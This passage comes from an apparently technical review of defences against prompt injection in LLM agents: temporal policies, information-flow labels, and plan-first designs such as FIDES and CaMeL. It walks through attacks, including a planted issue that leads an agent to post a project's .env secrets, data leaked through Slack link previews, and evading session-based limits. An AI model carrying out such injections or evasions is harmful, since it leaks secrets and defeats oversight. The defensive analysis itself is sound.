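| First | $0 | Allow | $2,000 | Allow |
| Second | $0 | Allow | $4,000 | Allow |
| Third | $0 | Allow | $6,000 | Deny |

A rule that adds up the responses lets $6,000 through because the responses don't exist yet. Adding up the requests instead blocks the third transfer, because that total includes the call under review. AgentCore handles only one authorisation at a time in each session, but this doesn't fix the faulty rule because the transfers themselves still overlap.

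AWS's sample rule for single-use approvals has the same weakness. It permits a transfer if no transfer has completed since the latest approval. Two transfers sent together would both pass on a single approval, because neither has completed when the engine checks the other. The rule can't simply check for requested transfers instead, because the transfer under review would then block itself. The harness would have to wait for each transfer to finish before sending the next.

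For the triage fence, the danger comes just after the model reads an issue. If the model proposes read_issue and write_file together, letting the write through would be harmless, because the model hasn't received the issue's text yet and the write can't contain instructions from it. But AWS notes that the gateway records a response shortly after the call completes, so a fast agent could read the issue and send a write before the response appears in the history. A read could also fail and still return an error message containing some of the attacker's text, and the history would then hold an error event but no response.

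A fence that matches requests covers both cases because it takes effect before any text arrives. But it also blocks the harmless simultaneous write, and it removes the agent's write access even after a failed read that returned nothing. AWS's documents differ on whether a denied call counts as a request. AWS describes request events as authorised calls, while its *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* includes denied attempts. Counting denied attempts would only make this fence stricter.

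A rule that requires an earlier step has to match the response from that step rather than the request. For example, if write_file depends on a maintainer's approval, the rule has to match a response whose output is "approved", because the request shows only that the agent asked for approval.

### Where the history begins and ends

A temporal rule covers one session, and the calling application decides what counts as a session. According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, the application generates a session ID and sends it with each request. A new ID starts an empty history, and no condition can look back more than 24 hours. If the engine has temporal rules, a request without an ID fails.

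AWS warns that a determined caller can get around a limit of three transfers per session by starting another session. The triage fence has the same weakness. An agent that can run its own code and reach the gateway with the project's credentials could read issue 42 under one session ID and call write_file under another.

The session ID has some protection against tampering. According to AWS's *Policy sessions and identity propagation*, the gateway ties each session to the caller's authenticated identity, so two users who send the same ID still have separate histories. When the agent itself runs on AgentCore, the platform carries the ID from the first request to later tool calls in a signed token that the agent's code can't change. On a gateway without authentication, everyone who sends the same ID shares one history, and AWS calls temporal rules there advisory only.

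Temporal rules can also fail without any attempt to evade them, because the engine's session is separate from the model's context. If an application creates a new session ID for every request, the engine never has any history to check. Changing the temporal rules also ends the sessions in progress, and AWS says to recover by starting a new session and resending the request. If a harness does this automatically in the middle of a conversation, the text of issue 42 stays in the model's context, but the engine loses its record of the read.

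The time limit has a similar effect, because the read_issue event drops out of the window after 24 hours and write_file becomes available again, even though the issue's text, or a summary of it, may still be in the context. This can happen within one session, since a session expires only after 24 hours without activity and can last for days if the agent keeps working. The Dogwood rule is therefore weaker than the formula G(untrusted_read → G ¬write_file), which has no time limit. To compensate, the harness has to clear the context whenever the session ID changes, and end both the session and the context within 24 hours of the first untrusted read.

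AWS recommends one session per conversation, which fits this requirement. Longer sessions suit other limits, such as a daily spending cap, but a fence would then carry over from one task to the next. A maintainer's agent that read a public issue in the morning couldn't fix an unrelated typo in the afternoon.

### What other systems' rules can express

Research systems place a similar check before each tool call but differ in what a rule can refer to. Progent, which is close to plain Cedar, restricts tool use through a special-purpose policy language. People or a language model write the rules for each task and set of tools. AgentSpec, a rule language from 2025, offers more outcomes than AgentCore's engine, which can only allow or deny. Each AgentSpec rule has a trigger, conditions and a response, and the response can be to stop the agent, ask the user or run a corrective action.

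An earlier system from the company Invariant Labs has rules about the whole trace. Balunović, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2024), in *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees*, describe an analyser that receives the trace so far, including the proposed call, and looks for any combination of events that matches a forbidden pattern. In its language, the triage fence is:

```
raise "No writes after reading an issue" if:
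    (c1: ToolCall) -> (c2: ToolCall)
    c1 is tool:read_issue
    c2 is tool:write_file
```

The arrow comes from research on information flow, but it is defined to mean only that the first event happened before the second. The rule therefore blocks a write even if it has nothing to do with the issue. To distinguish such a write from one that depends on the issue, a rule must track where data came from, as label-based rules do.

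Invariant's conditions can also call any Python function, so a rule can depend on what a call contains. One sample rule stops a coding agent from pushing a file to GitHub if the contents match the format of an OpenAI access key. Other rules can use a classifier that detects personal information or unsafe code. The "formal guarantee" in the title is then that the analyser blocks every trace that matches a rule, but if the classifier misses a secret, the rule doesn't match and the call goes through.

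Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, use an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical and arithmetical constraints can all be true together. Their system translates each proposed action into such constraints. If s is the current state, a the action, δ the function that gives the next state, and Φ the set of safety rules, the monitor lets the action run only if:

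δ(s, a) ⊨ Φ

The state after the action must satisfy every rule. This suits limits that depend on several quantities at once, such as balances after a series of transfers. Wu and colleagues assume the model itself is the attacker and knows all the rules. In a test with multi-step transfers, no attack succeeded and the system blocked no legitimate action. The core calculation took 0.44 milliseconds on average. In a simulated company network, the system also withstood a 12-round attempt to extract data. Two scenarios are a narrow test, though, and the guarantee assumes that the translation is faithful, the rules are right and the agent can't get around the monitor.

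All these systems need someone to state what is forbidden. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Iqbal and colleagues, 2026) tries to learn it instead. The paper criticises Progent for needing a separate policy for each agent and manual edits to rules written by a language model. Agent-Sentry records legitimate runs, including where each argument came from, and treats departures from those patterns as suspicious. A classifier first sorts each proposed action into allowed, blocked or ambiguous. For ambiguous actions, a fixed check lets through familiar argument values from trusted sources. A language model judges the remaining ambiguous actions by comparing them with the user's request.

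On two sets of simulated tasks, AgentDojo and AgentDyn, Agent-Sentry blocked 94.3% of the injections that would otherwise have succeeded and allowed about 95% of legitimate runs. It can help against mistakes nobody thought to forbid, but it missed 5.7% of those injections, so it doesn't make any tool unreachable. It also relies on the agent to report where its arguments came from, and Sequeira and colleagues acknowledge that they can't fully trust those reports. Because Agent-Sentry learns from what an agent usually does, it would keep allowing a dangerous action that a project has always allowed.

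### Allowed calls that serve an attacker

The main objection to an external policy is that an attacker may need only the calls the policy allows. Balunović and colleagues found an example in two widely used agent systems. A user asks the agent to read customer feedback in a spreadsheet and send the user a summary on Slack, a workplace messaging service. Both steps look internal, and only the user receives the message. But one customer's feedback contains an instruction to add to the summary a link that encodes the spreadsheet's contents in its web address. Slack automatically opens links to display a preview, so the contents go to the attacker's server as soon as the message arrives. The providers fixed the flaw after the researchers reported it.

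One reply is to write a narrower rule. Balunović and colleagues' rule blocks a Slack message only if the agent has read a document and the message has link previews turned on, so the agent can still send the summary with previews off. The rule works however the attacker words the instruction, whereas an injection detector the researchers tried passed the hostile feedback and flagged a harmless review. But writing the rule required knowing about link previews.

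Another approach is to accept that some attacks will get through and limit what they can do. Spending caps do this, and so do rules that require an argument in a tool call to come from an earlier result. In AWS's example, the agent can send money only to an account that a lookup returned in the same session. This stops the agent from using an account number that the model or an attacker made up. It doesn't stop an attacker who is also a customer, because the injected text can tell the agent to look up the attacker's account and then pay it, and the rule allows both calls.

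A policy can also examine the text of a call. Dogwood rules can call AWS's content classifiers and deny the request if the score passes a threshold. The decision then depends on a classifier, and Nasr and colleagues found that classifiers are vulnerable to adaptive attacks. A rule can also require a person's approval for the riskiest calls, but this causes the approval fatigue that AWS wanted to avoid.

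AWS acknowledges that some requirements, such as acting in the customer's best financial interest, can't become rules about tool calls. It would leave that one to the agent's instructions, training and evaluation. Sequeira and colleagues exclude attacks that change only what the agent tells its user, such as a false summary of an email, because they involve no tool call to block.

The triage agent posts its replies through a tool, so the gateway can block them, but fixed rules can't separate good advice from bad. A project that wants its agent to answer strangers can have a maintainer approve each comment, or it can allow post_comment without review and rely on the model's training for the wording.

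## The view that data should carry labels

A fence can't distinguish a write that depends on issue 42 from an unrelated one, because it doesn't track where data came from. Information-flow control tracks this with labels. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes three steps: labeling everything the agent takes in, giving anything derived from that data a label at least as strict, and checking the labels before each tool call. The model plays no part in the check, and a stranger who writes an issue can't change the label the harness puts on it.

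### Labels and how they combine

A label has an integrity part, which records how far to trust the source, and a confidentiality part, which records who may see the data. In the simplest scheme each part has two values: trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high). Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, order these values by a relation written ⊑, which reads "may flow to":

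T ⊑ U and L ⊑ H

Trusted data may go anywhere that accepts untrusted data, and public data may go anywhere that accepts secrets, but not the reverse. A full label such as (U, L) may flow to another label if each part may flow to the corresponding part.

When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result takes the join of their labels, written ⊔. This is the least restrictive label that both may flow to. Combining a stranger's public issue with one of the project's private files gives:

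(U, L) ⊔ (T, H) = (U, H)

A confidentiality label can also be a set of permitted readers, with the join being the intersection of the sets. Microsoft gives the example of Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't yet authorised to see the figures, has also written. Once the agent has read both messages, anything it writes has the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't reply to Marco without asking. This prevents a leak that a careless agent could cause even without an attacker. If Priya had copied Marco in, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have replied to him.

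### Why one untrusted item taints the rest

In an ordinary program, the code shows which inputs a result depends on. A model's output can depend on any token in its context, and nobody can read off which tokens mattered. The cautious assumption is that all of them did. If the context holds messages m₁ to mₙ with labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ, then:

label of the output = ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ

The output then becomes part of the context and passes its label to the next output. A join never makes a label less strict, so a context that has become untrusted stays untrusted. After the triage agent reads issue 42, everything the model produces in that run is labeled untrusted, including a fix for a typo that the maintainer pointed out.

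The context label works as a prompt class that changes during the run. If ℓ is the current label, A(ℓ) is the set of tools whose rules accept ℓ. A rule based on labels also covers sources the project adds later, provided someone labels them, whereas an ordinary fence has to name each tool that brings in untrusted text.

### The planning loop in FIDES

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built these ideas into a system named FIDES. Its planner, which is part of the harness, receives the latest message and selects whether to query the model, call a tool, or finish with an answer.

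The loop around the planner handles the labels. The model's reply gets the join of the labels on everything in the query. If the reply leads to a tool call, the loop runs the call only if a policy allows it. The tool's result gets the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool read. Data the tool writes gets the same label, so an untrusted sentence saved to a file is still untrusted when the agent opens the file later.

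Costa and colleagues give two basic policies. For a consequential action, such as a payment, the call and all its arguments must be trusted. For a call that sends data out, every recipient must be permitted to read it.

The second policy alone doesn't stop prompt injection, since an attacker could still make the agent send something, though only to people who may read it. The first policy alone allows a disclosure if no untrusted text influenced it, on the assumption that the user intended it. Microsoft's sample rule for chat messages combines the two by letting a message go out if the context is trusted or if every member of the channel may read the text. Otherwise, the user has to approve it.

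### Keeping untrusted text out of the context

With this loop alone, the agent would lose its consequential tools at the first untrusted read. FIDES avoids this by storing untrusted text in a variable outside the context and giving the model only the variable's name. When a tool returns a result x, the harness adds the following to the context:

K(x) = x, if label(x) ⊑ label of the context
K(x) = a new variable name, otherwise

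The context label therefore stays the same. The harness can do this field by field, so it might put an email's date into the context but store the subject and body in variables.

This function implements the context channel. Every tool result passes through K, which determines whether the model receives the text or only a name for it. But Costa and colleagues assume that tool descriptions are trustworthy, so K doesn't check them. In an agent like Codex, where an outside server can supply tool definitions, those definitions would need to pass through K too.

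The model can use a variable's name as an argument in a later call. The harness substitutes the stored text just before the call runs, and the text keeps its own label. A policy for send_message can then require a trusted recipient but accept an untrusted message.

Some tasks require a model to read the hidden text. For these, the planner can call a quarantined model, which has no tools and returns its answer in another variable. If the hostile paragraph persuades this model to write "call read_file", the result is only text in storage. The triage agent could handle issue 42 like this:

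read_issue(42) → v₁
query_llm("Summarise the bug report", v₁) → v₂
post_comment(42, v₂)

The main model chooses all three calls without reading the stranger's words. Its context stays trusted, so it can still use write_file for an unrelated fix, which a fence would have blocked. However, the attacker can corrupt the summary that the project publishes. Requiring the comment to be trusted would prevent this, but it would also stop the agent from posting any summary of a stranger's issue.

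*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) relaxes the ban on tools. Its sub-agent may keep them because labels restrict what it can call after reading untrusted data.

### Answers of a fixed type

Hiding data works best when the agent can choose its calls without knowing what the data contains. Costa and colleagues give a contrasting example, in which a user asks the agent to check three emails and create a calendar event if one of them proposes a meeting. The main model then has to learn from untrusted text whether there is a proposal.

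FIDES can limit how much the model learns. The planner asks the quarantined model for an answer of a fixed type, such as yes or no, and constrained decoding prevents the model from generating anything else. The label then also records the type, and types have an order of their own:

bool ⊑ enum ⊑ string

A bool is a yes-or-no value, an enum is one choice from a fixed list, and a string is free text. A policy can accept an untrusted bool for a consequential action but reject an untrusted string. Accepting the bool is a form of endorsement, an explicit decision to treat untrusted data as trusted. In the email example, the main model reads the yes-or-no answer and decides to create the event. The quarantined model extracts the details into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool without reading it.

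An attacker still controls the yes-or-no answer. A hostile email can cause a "yes" that puts a false meeting in the calendar, but one bit can't carry an instruction to send the user's files somewhere. Several answers together can carry more, and the type label doesn't show how many were combined, because the join of two bools is still bool.

The main model can also read a whole variable, and its context then takes on the variable's label. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) notes that CaMeL, a related system that fixes its plan in advance, doesn't offer this choice.

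Hiding text in variables is not enough to make a tool unreachable, because the model can open the variables. On the simulated tasks in AgentDojo, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent and 21 against FIDES with its policy checks switched off. With the checks on, none succeeded. That version of FIDES didn't include constrained decoding, so the result doesn't test the typed answers.

### What the theorem covers

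Costa and colleagues prove that the labelled loop can enforce explicit secrecy. Take one particular sequence of steps that the agent performs, and let g be its combined effect on stored data. Let d₁ and d₂ be two versions of that data that agree on everything public and may differ in their secrets. Then:

d₁ =ₗ d₂ ⇒ g(d₁) =ₗ g(d₂)

where =ₗ means "agrees on all public data". If the steps stay the same, changing the secrets can't change anything that the public can see.

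The condition about the steps matters because a secret can also influence which steps the agent takes. Suppose an agent reads a confidential test result and posts a fixed public notice only if the result is bad. The notice contains no secret data, but its appearance reveals the result. Explicit secrecy permits this leak. Noninterference would forbid it, but Costa and colleagues consider that property too restrictive, since in practice the agent could not use any tool with publicly visible effects after using one that might have read a secret. Their proof also treats the model as deterministic and leaves out side channels such as timing.

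Tracking labels during a run can therefore enforce both explicit secrecy and safety properties. The rule for consequential actions is a safety property because a single consequential call that runs with an untrusted label violates it. The loop could also keep the whole labelled history and check rules about the order of events, including the rules in Invariant's language. Neither explicit secrecy nor safety properties cover whether a summary is accurate or whether someone labelled the data correctly.

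### The triage attack in Agent Framework

On 20 May 2026, Microsoft released an experimental version of FIDES in Agent Framework, its software for building agents. The triage agent is Microsoft's own demonstration. Its read_issue tool labels the text of a public issue as untrusted and public, and read_file labels every file as trusted and private. The write_file tool will not run in an untrusted context, and post_comment will not run in a private one.

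In the demonstration, Microsoft switches off the hiding of untrusted text, so the main model reads the attacker's paragraph and may obey it. The run then goes as follows:

| Event | Decision | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user asks for triage | None needed | Trusted, public |
| read_issue(42) | Allowed | Untrusted, public |
| read_file(".env") | Allowed | Untrusted, private |
| post_comment(42, contents of .env) | Refused | Untrusted, private |

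The secret enters the context but can't leave through the public comment. If the attack instead tries to overwrite the build configuration, the harness refuses write_file as soon as the issue arrives, because the context is already untrusted. Neither decision depends on whether the model recognised the attack.

In this configuration, when a call is blocked, the system asks the user to approve it and shows the tool and the label that caused the block. The user can override the block, so the tools are unreachable only if the user never approves a bad call. Microsoft's documentation describes another setting that blocks the call outright and a trial mode that tracks labels without blocking anything.

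Microsoft's release post describes post_comment as unavailable while any untrusted content is in the context, but the example's code restricts only confidentiality. After reading issue 42, the agent can still post a public comment that the attacker dictated, unless the project also applies the restriction on untrusted contexts to post_comment.

The example is too strict in another respect. The agent has read_file so that it can quote relevant code in its replies, but the tool labels every file private, so reading any source file blocks the reply. Agent Framework allows a separate label on each item a tool returns, so the project could label published source code public and .env private, though someone would then have to classify the files correctly.

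By default, the issue's text goes into a variable hidden from the main model. The main model can process the text only through the quarantined model or by opening the variable, which leaves an entry in the audit log. The quarantined model's summary has to stay in a variable too, because a summary can repeat the attacker's instructions.

Programs can also pass labels to each other. Microsoft worked with GitHub on an option that labels the results from GitHub's MCP server. It marks data from public repositories as public and untrusted, and data from private ones as private and trusted. An experimental setting in GitHub's Copilot command-line tool keeps a label for the context and updates it with each result. A policy can then stop an agent from reading both a public issue and a private repository and then posting publicly, which is the pattern behind GitLost. An agent that works only with public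 repositories, or only with private ones, can finish without interruption.

### Over-tainting

Strict labels can block a lot of harmless work. Microsoft acknowledges that once an issue's text enters the context, the rest of the run stays untrusted unless someone explicitly drops the text. This is known as label creep in older work on information flow. The maintainer must then approve every later file change, which causes approval fatigue again.

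One remedy is to divide the work among several agents so that a label on one doesn't spread to the others. Gregory, Domico and colleagues simulated this without a language model in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026). They generated more than 9,000 tasks of 4 to 20 tool calls each and distributed the calls among 5 to 20 agents. An agent that received or passed on sensitive data kept the sensitive label permanently. The researchers measured the share of tool calls that introduced a sensitive label or ran under one.

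Labels spread least when agents could communicate directly. In a star layout, where messages pass through a central agent, that agent soon picks up the label and passes it on. With 5 agents and 4 sensitive calls per task, the star layout had about 5 percentage points more affected calls than direct communication. Using more agents and giving the sensitive tools to only a few of them also helped, though the number of connections to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. No layout eliminated the problem, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a way to remove labels.

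*APPA* (2026) keeps strict propagation and adds a way to recover when a call is blocked. The agent can do risky reading in a separate branch with its own label, while all branches share one record of the actions taken. The model can suggest how to recover, but it can't authorise a call. The guarantee still holds because the harness always applies the labels on text the model has read.

The other remedies keep only the labels of those parts of the context judged to have influenced a call. A wrong judgment can remove a label that should have stayed, so the guarantee depends on what happens after such a mistake.

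### Removing what a call doesn't need

Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, handle such mistakes by deleting text. Before the model acts, a screener selects the parts of the history that seem relevant to the next step. The harness joins their labels into one label, ℓ*, and blanks out every part m of the history that fails this test:

label(m) ⊑ ℓ*

The model then acts on what remains, and the policy checks its tool calls against ℓ*. Suppose the maintainer asks for an unrelated typo fix after the agent has read issue 42. If the screener selects only trusted text, ℓ* is trusted and the policy allows write_file. The harness blanks out the issue, so it can't influence the write.

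The guarantee holds even if the screener chooses wrongly. If the screener overlooks the issue when the task needs it, the model won't have the text and may fail the task. If hostile text gets the screener to select it, ℓ* becomes untrusted and write_file needs the user's approval. The screener's choice depends on the whole history, so the pattern of deletions could reveal a little about a secret, but explicit secrecy doesn't cover such indirect flows.

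Zhong and colleagues tried two screeners. One is a language model that judges relevance. The other runs a small open model, measures how much its output attends to each part of the history, and feeds these measurements to a trained classifier. Each roughly doubled token use on AgentDojo's banking tasks. The system blocked every attack that violated its policy, but in one test it didn't track the injected text because the text was in material labeled as trusted.

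### Reconstructing the flow from the trace

*AGENTARMOR* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) treats an agent's runtime trace as a program to analyse. The system turns the trace into a graph whose nodes include prompts, tool names, arguments and results, and whose edges show the dependencies between them. A registry adds effects that the trace doesn't show, such as the folder that a git_clone call creates. Labels then spread along the edges, and a checker stops the agent if secret data reaches a public destination or untrusted data reaches a trusted one.

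The graph gives each argument its own label, so one untrusted result needn't taint every later call. It can also follow data through a file that one tool writes and another reads. But a language model infers many of the edges from the earlier prompts and results, by identifying which ones led to the current action. If it attributes an injected write_file call to the maintainer's request, the graph lacks the edge from the issue and the checker allows the call.

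In such a case, RTBAS would have removed the issue from the context, but AgentArmor leaves it there, and it has already influenced the call. The guarantee therefore fails if the analyser makes a mistake. On AgentDojo, AgentArmor reduced the attack success rate from 41% to 3%.

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses ordinary code to build a provenance graph, a record of where values came from. Just before a tool runs, the system freezes the call and compares its arguments with previously recorded values. A match links the argument to its source. The system then looks for paths from untrusted or secret data to an unsafe effect, and finds the set of links with the lowest total weight that it can cut to remove them all. Cutting these links often means blocking the call. A second check determines whether the user's original request authorised the call's effects.

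The second check can catch an attack that the graph misses. If the model rephrases the attacker's text, the new wording may not match any recorded value, and the graph would then have no link to the issue. But a request to summarise an issue doesn't authorise a change to the build configuration, so the call still fails.

Li and colleagues prove that a harmful chain of events can't complete if the graph represents every link and the harness carries out the cut. The guarantee doesn't cover text that the model has rewritten or effects that a tool doesn't declare, and it is weaker than noninterference. The proof also applies to a stricter version of PACE than the one tested. If the user's request authorised a call, the tested version can restore it after the path check blocks it. It can also repair a call without checking the result again. With the path check alone, agents couldn't finish many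 ordinary tasks.

The guarantee therefore holds for the tested version only when its final action happens to meet the theorem's conditions. Even so, an automated search that adapted to the defence succeeded on none of 30 AgentDojo targets, compared with 21 of 30 without a defence. In the main tests, the highest attack success rate on AgentDojo ranged from 0% to 8.1% across models.

In the same experiments, between 24% and 40% of attacks succeeded against FIDES on WASP, a set of web tasks. That was a higher rate than against an agent with no defence. FIDES got its perfect score on AgentDojo with labels and policies that Costa and colleagues wrote for those tasks, so the result doesn't necessarily carry over to other settings.

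### Measuring influence in bits

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests replacing hard labels with soft ones that estimate how much information an output carries about each input. It also raises the open question of how finely to divide the context, since a single stream of tokens mixes text from many sources.

*GIF*, short for geometric information flow (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026), offers a way to calculate such amounts. A model represents each token as a list of numbers, called its embedding. The method calculates how much the next token Y would reveal about small random changes U to the embeddings of one passage. This quantity is the mutual information I(U; Y), which is zero if the passage has no effect on the output.

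Calculating it exactly is impractical for a large model, so Štorek and colleagues substitute a simpler channel that behaves the same way for small changes. If τ is the variance of the changes and the matrix A describes how strongly they move the model's output, the simpler channel transmits:

½ log det(I + τAAᵀ)

Here I is the identity matrix. The authors prove, with a proof that the Lean proof checker has verified, that their measure satisfies:

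I(U; Y) ≤ GIF(τ) + o(τ) as τ → 0

The last term shrinks faster than τ, so for small enough changes the measure doesn't meaningfully underestimate the flow. In the paper's example, a job applicant's CV contains an instruction to recommend them at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. The measure attributes 82 bits of flow to the injected instruction, 27 to the employer's hiring criteria and 16 to the neutral text. A policy could block the recommendation or send the suspicious passage to another model for review, and ignore passages with little influence.

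This reduces over-tainting but greatly weakens the guarantee. The theorem covers tiny changes around one fixed prompt, whereas an attacker can replace whole sentences. Someone also has to choose how many bits of flow to allow, and a flow below that limit can still matter. When developers can't access the main model's internals, they can measure the flow in a smaller model. That worked well in the experiments, but the proof doesn't extend from one model to another.

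*Sightline* (2026) sets an error rate in advance and calibrates its estimates to meet it. With a target of 5%, it removed half of the unnecessary labels from an agent built on Qwen3-8B, with a miss rate of 3.9% of episodes. It kept the labels in almost all attack cases, and no attack call passed the integrity policy in the tests. A 5% target still allows some real flows to lose their labels, and a single lost label can make write_file reachable.

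## The view that the plan should be fixed before untrusted text is read

Labels restrict what an agent can do after untrusted text enters its context. Another approach is to fix the agent's actions beforehand. A model plans the whole sequence of tool calls based on the user's trusted request, and ordinary code then carries it out. Injected text can't add a call because the sequence is already set when that text is read.

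Let u be the request, p(u) the plan a model writes for it, and T(p(u)) the set of tools in that plan. Then, at every step i of the run:

eᵢ = exec(t, a)  ⇒  t ∈ T(p(u))

The plan depends only on u, so nothing in issue 42 can enlarge the set. If the harness also has a policy for each prompt class, it can check that T(p(u)) ⊆ A(c) before making the first call.

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) call this property control-flow integrity, a term from older work on protecting programs. Under their definition, a plan can branch on tool results, so outside text can influence which planned path the agent takes but can't create a new one.

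### From two models to a program

The approach grew out of a blog post, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which proposed a split between a privileged model that has tools and a quarantined model that reads untrusted text. FIDES later adopted this split. In Willison's version, the privileged model still picks one action at a time, after learning that the previous one has finished.

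Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text through removes the protection. It also relies on the user's request being trustworthy, which it isn't if someone tricks the user into pasting in hostile text.

In 2025 Debenedetti and colleagues, at Google DeepMind, pointed out another weakness, which is that hostile text can change the data used in a planned call. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, but the quarantined model has to extract the address. A hostile line in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The assistant then makes the planned calls but sends the document to the attacker.

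### How CaMeL would handle issue 42

Their answer was CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", which they described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. As Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains, the privileged model turns the request into a program in a restricted form of Python. Suppose a maintainer asks the triage agent to reply to issue 42 with a summary of the bug and the relevant code. The program could look like this:

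```
issue = read_issue(42)
path = query_quarantined_llm(
    f"Which source file does this report concern? {issue}",
    output_schema=str
)
code = read_file(path)
reply = query_quarantined_llm(
    f"Summarise the bug and quote the relevant lines. {issue} {code}",
    output_schema=str
)
post_comment(42, reply)
```

A custom interpreter runs the program one operation at a time. It calls the tools, sends text to the quarantined model when the program requires it, and stores the results in the variables. The privileged model has already finished and never receives the values. Since write_file isn't in the program, the hostile paragraph can't cause a write, whatever it contains.

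The paragraph can still do harm if it gives .env as the location of the bug. If the quarantined model returns that path, the agent reads the file and posts its contents, as in the original attack, and the plan permits every step. CaMeL defends against this by attaching capabilities to each value, which are tags that work much like the labels in FIDES. The interpreter checks these tags before each tool call. In Willison's example, an email goes out without the user's approval only if the recipient's address is trusted.

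For the triage agent, a rule that post_comment accepts only public data would stop the leak, as it did with FIDES. A rule that read_file accepts only trusted paths would stop it one step earlier, but would also prevent the agent from following a legitimate report to the right file.

The guarantee about secrets therefore depends on policies that someone has to write and maintain. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge this burden and the risk of approval fatigue. The tags must also cover information that leaks through which branch the plan takes. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) confirms in a formal model that an injection cannot add calls to a dual-LLM agent, but finds that tags that track only data are not enough for every plan. CaMeL has a strict mode designed to close this gap.

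Many triage agents start automatically when a stranger opens an issue. The trusted request is then the project's own instruction, which is the same for every issue, so the project could have the model write the program once, review it by hand, and reuse it.

### Planning without reading the tool descriptions

CaMeL's privileged model reads the descriptions of the available tools and treats them as trusted. That is risky if the tools are third-party apps, because an app's developer writes its description. Li, Mallick and colleagues presented a design called *ACE* at the NDSS security symposium in February 2026. Its first planning stage has no information about the installed apps.

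They motivate it with attacks on IsolateGPT, an earlier system that runs each app in isolation. In one attack, a user wants to compare fares from two apps, MetroHail and QuickRide. QuickRide's description contains an instruction to leave MetroHail out. The planner follows this instruction, so the user receives only QuickRide's fare.

ACE first writes an abstract plan. The planner receives the request and, if needed, a trusted note about the environment. It defines hypothetical apps, each with a name, a description, and input and output types. For issue 42, these might be an IssueReader and a CommentPoster. The planner then writes a short program that calls the apps. The program can contain branches and loops, but ACE restricts the language so that programs are easier to analyse.

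Next, a model matches each invented app to an installed one. It judges every pair separately, so QuickRide's description can't affect MetroHail's chances. A malicious app can still be matched if its description presents it as suitable. In 2,000 trials on one benchmark, ACE called an attacker's app three times, each time because the app suited the task.

ACE then checks the flow of data through the whole plan before running any of it. Each app has a clearance, such as a set of permitted categories like "medical", "financial" and "personal", and the user marks how sensitive the request is. If the plan passes x₁ to xₙ to app f, the check requires:

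label(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ) ⊑ clearance(f)

A plan that loads bank details and passes them to an email app with only the "personal" clearance fails this check. The analysis also covers indirect leaks by giving a secret's label to every variable set inside a branch that depends on that secret. It analyzes each loop repeatedly until the labels stop changing. If no combination of installed apps passes, ACE stops with an error. FIDES and CaMeL check each call as it comes up, so they may discover a forbidden flow only after earlier calls have taken effect.

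Finally, ACE runs the program in a container that has no direct access to files or apps. The program sends each request to an orchestrator, which starts the app in its own container with only the permissions it needs and checks the type of the result. In a test of the fare comparison, QuickRide returned an instruction to report false fares. ACE recorded a type error for QuickRide and still displayed MetroHail's fare.

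ACE ran no attacker's app in any of the 1,054 cases of InjecAgent, a set of prompt injection tests. It called the app the user needed in 60% to 85% of those cases, depending on the models. ACE handles only single requests so far. Li and colleagues do not formally guarantee that the check catches every leak, because Python's behaviour is too complex to analyse fully.

### What the published patterns forbid

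CaMeL and ACE are two of many ways to keep untrusted text away from decisions. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, think it unlikely that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees with current models. They recommend building agents that can do less. Once such an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any consequential action. They describe six patterns:

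| Pattern | What it forbids | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | Returning the results of actions to the model | A chatbot chooses from a fixed list of actions, such as fetching a link to the last order |
| Plan-then-execute | Changing the list of calls in response to a result | An assistant reads today's calendar and emails it to a named person |
| LLM map-reduce | Letting a model that reads one document use harmful tools or affect how other documents are processed | A separate model checks each file and answers only whether it is an invoice |
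| Dual LLM | Showing untrusted text to the model that has tools | The privileged model passes on an email address by its variable name |
| Code-then-execute | Changing the program in response to a result | CaMeL |
| Context-minimisation | Keeping the user's prompt in the context after it has served its purpose | A chatbot turns a request for a car quote into a database query, then answers without the prompt |

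The patterns leave an attacker with different amounts of influence. In the invoice example, a hostile file can only cause itself to be counted as an invoice. In the calendar example, a hostile entry can rewrite the whole email but can't change who receives it. A fixed plan doesn't stop attacks in the user's own prompt, but context-minimisation addresses them.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten kinds of agent. For the software engineering agent, which most resembles the triage agent, they list only the dual-LLM pattern.

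### Values the attacker can still choose

An attacker who can't add a tool call can try to change the values in the calls the task already needs. Zhang, Bertran and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Instruction Override*, built 90 test cases around this idea at Amazon. In one, a user asks an agent to resolve a dispute over a damaged item and to take the refund amount from the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence includes a claim that policy adds a $175 repair cost, for a total of $1,074.99. Text like this can be a plain factual claim, with no instruction for a detector to find.

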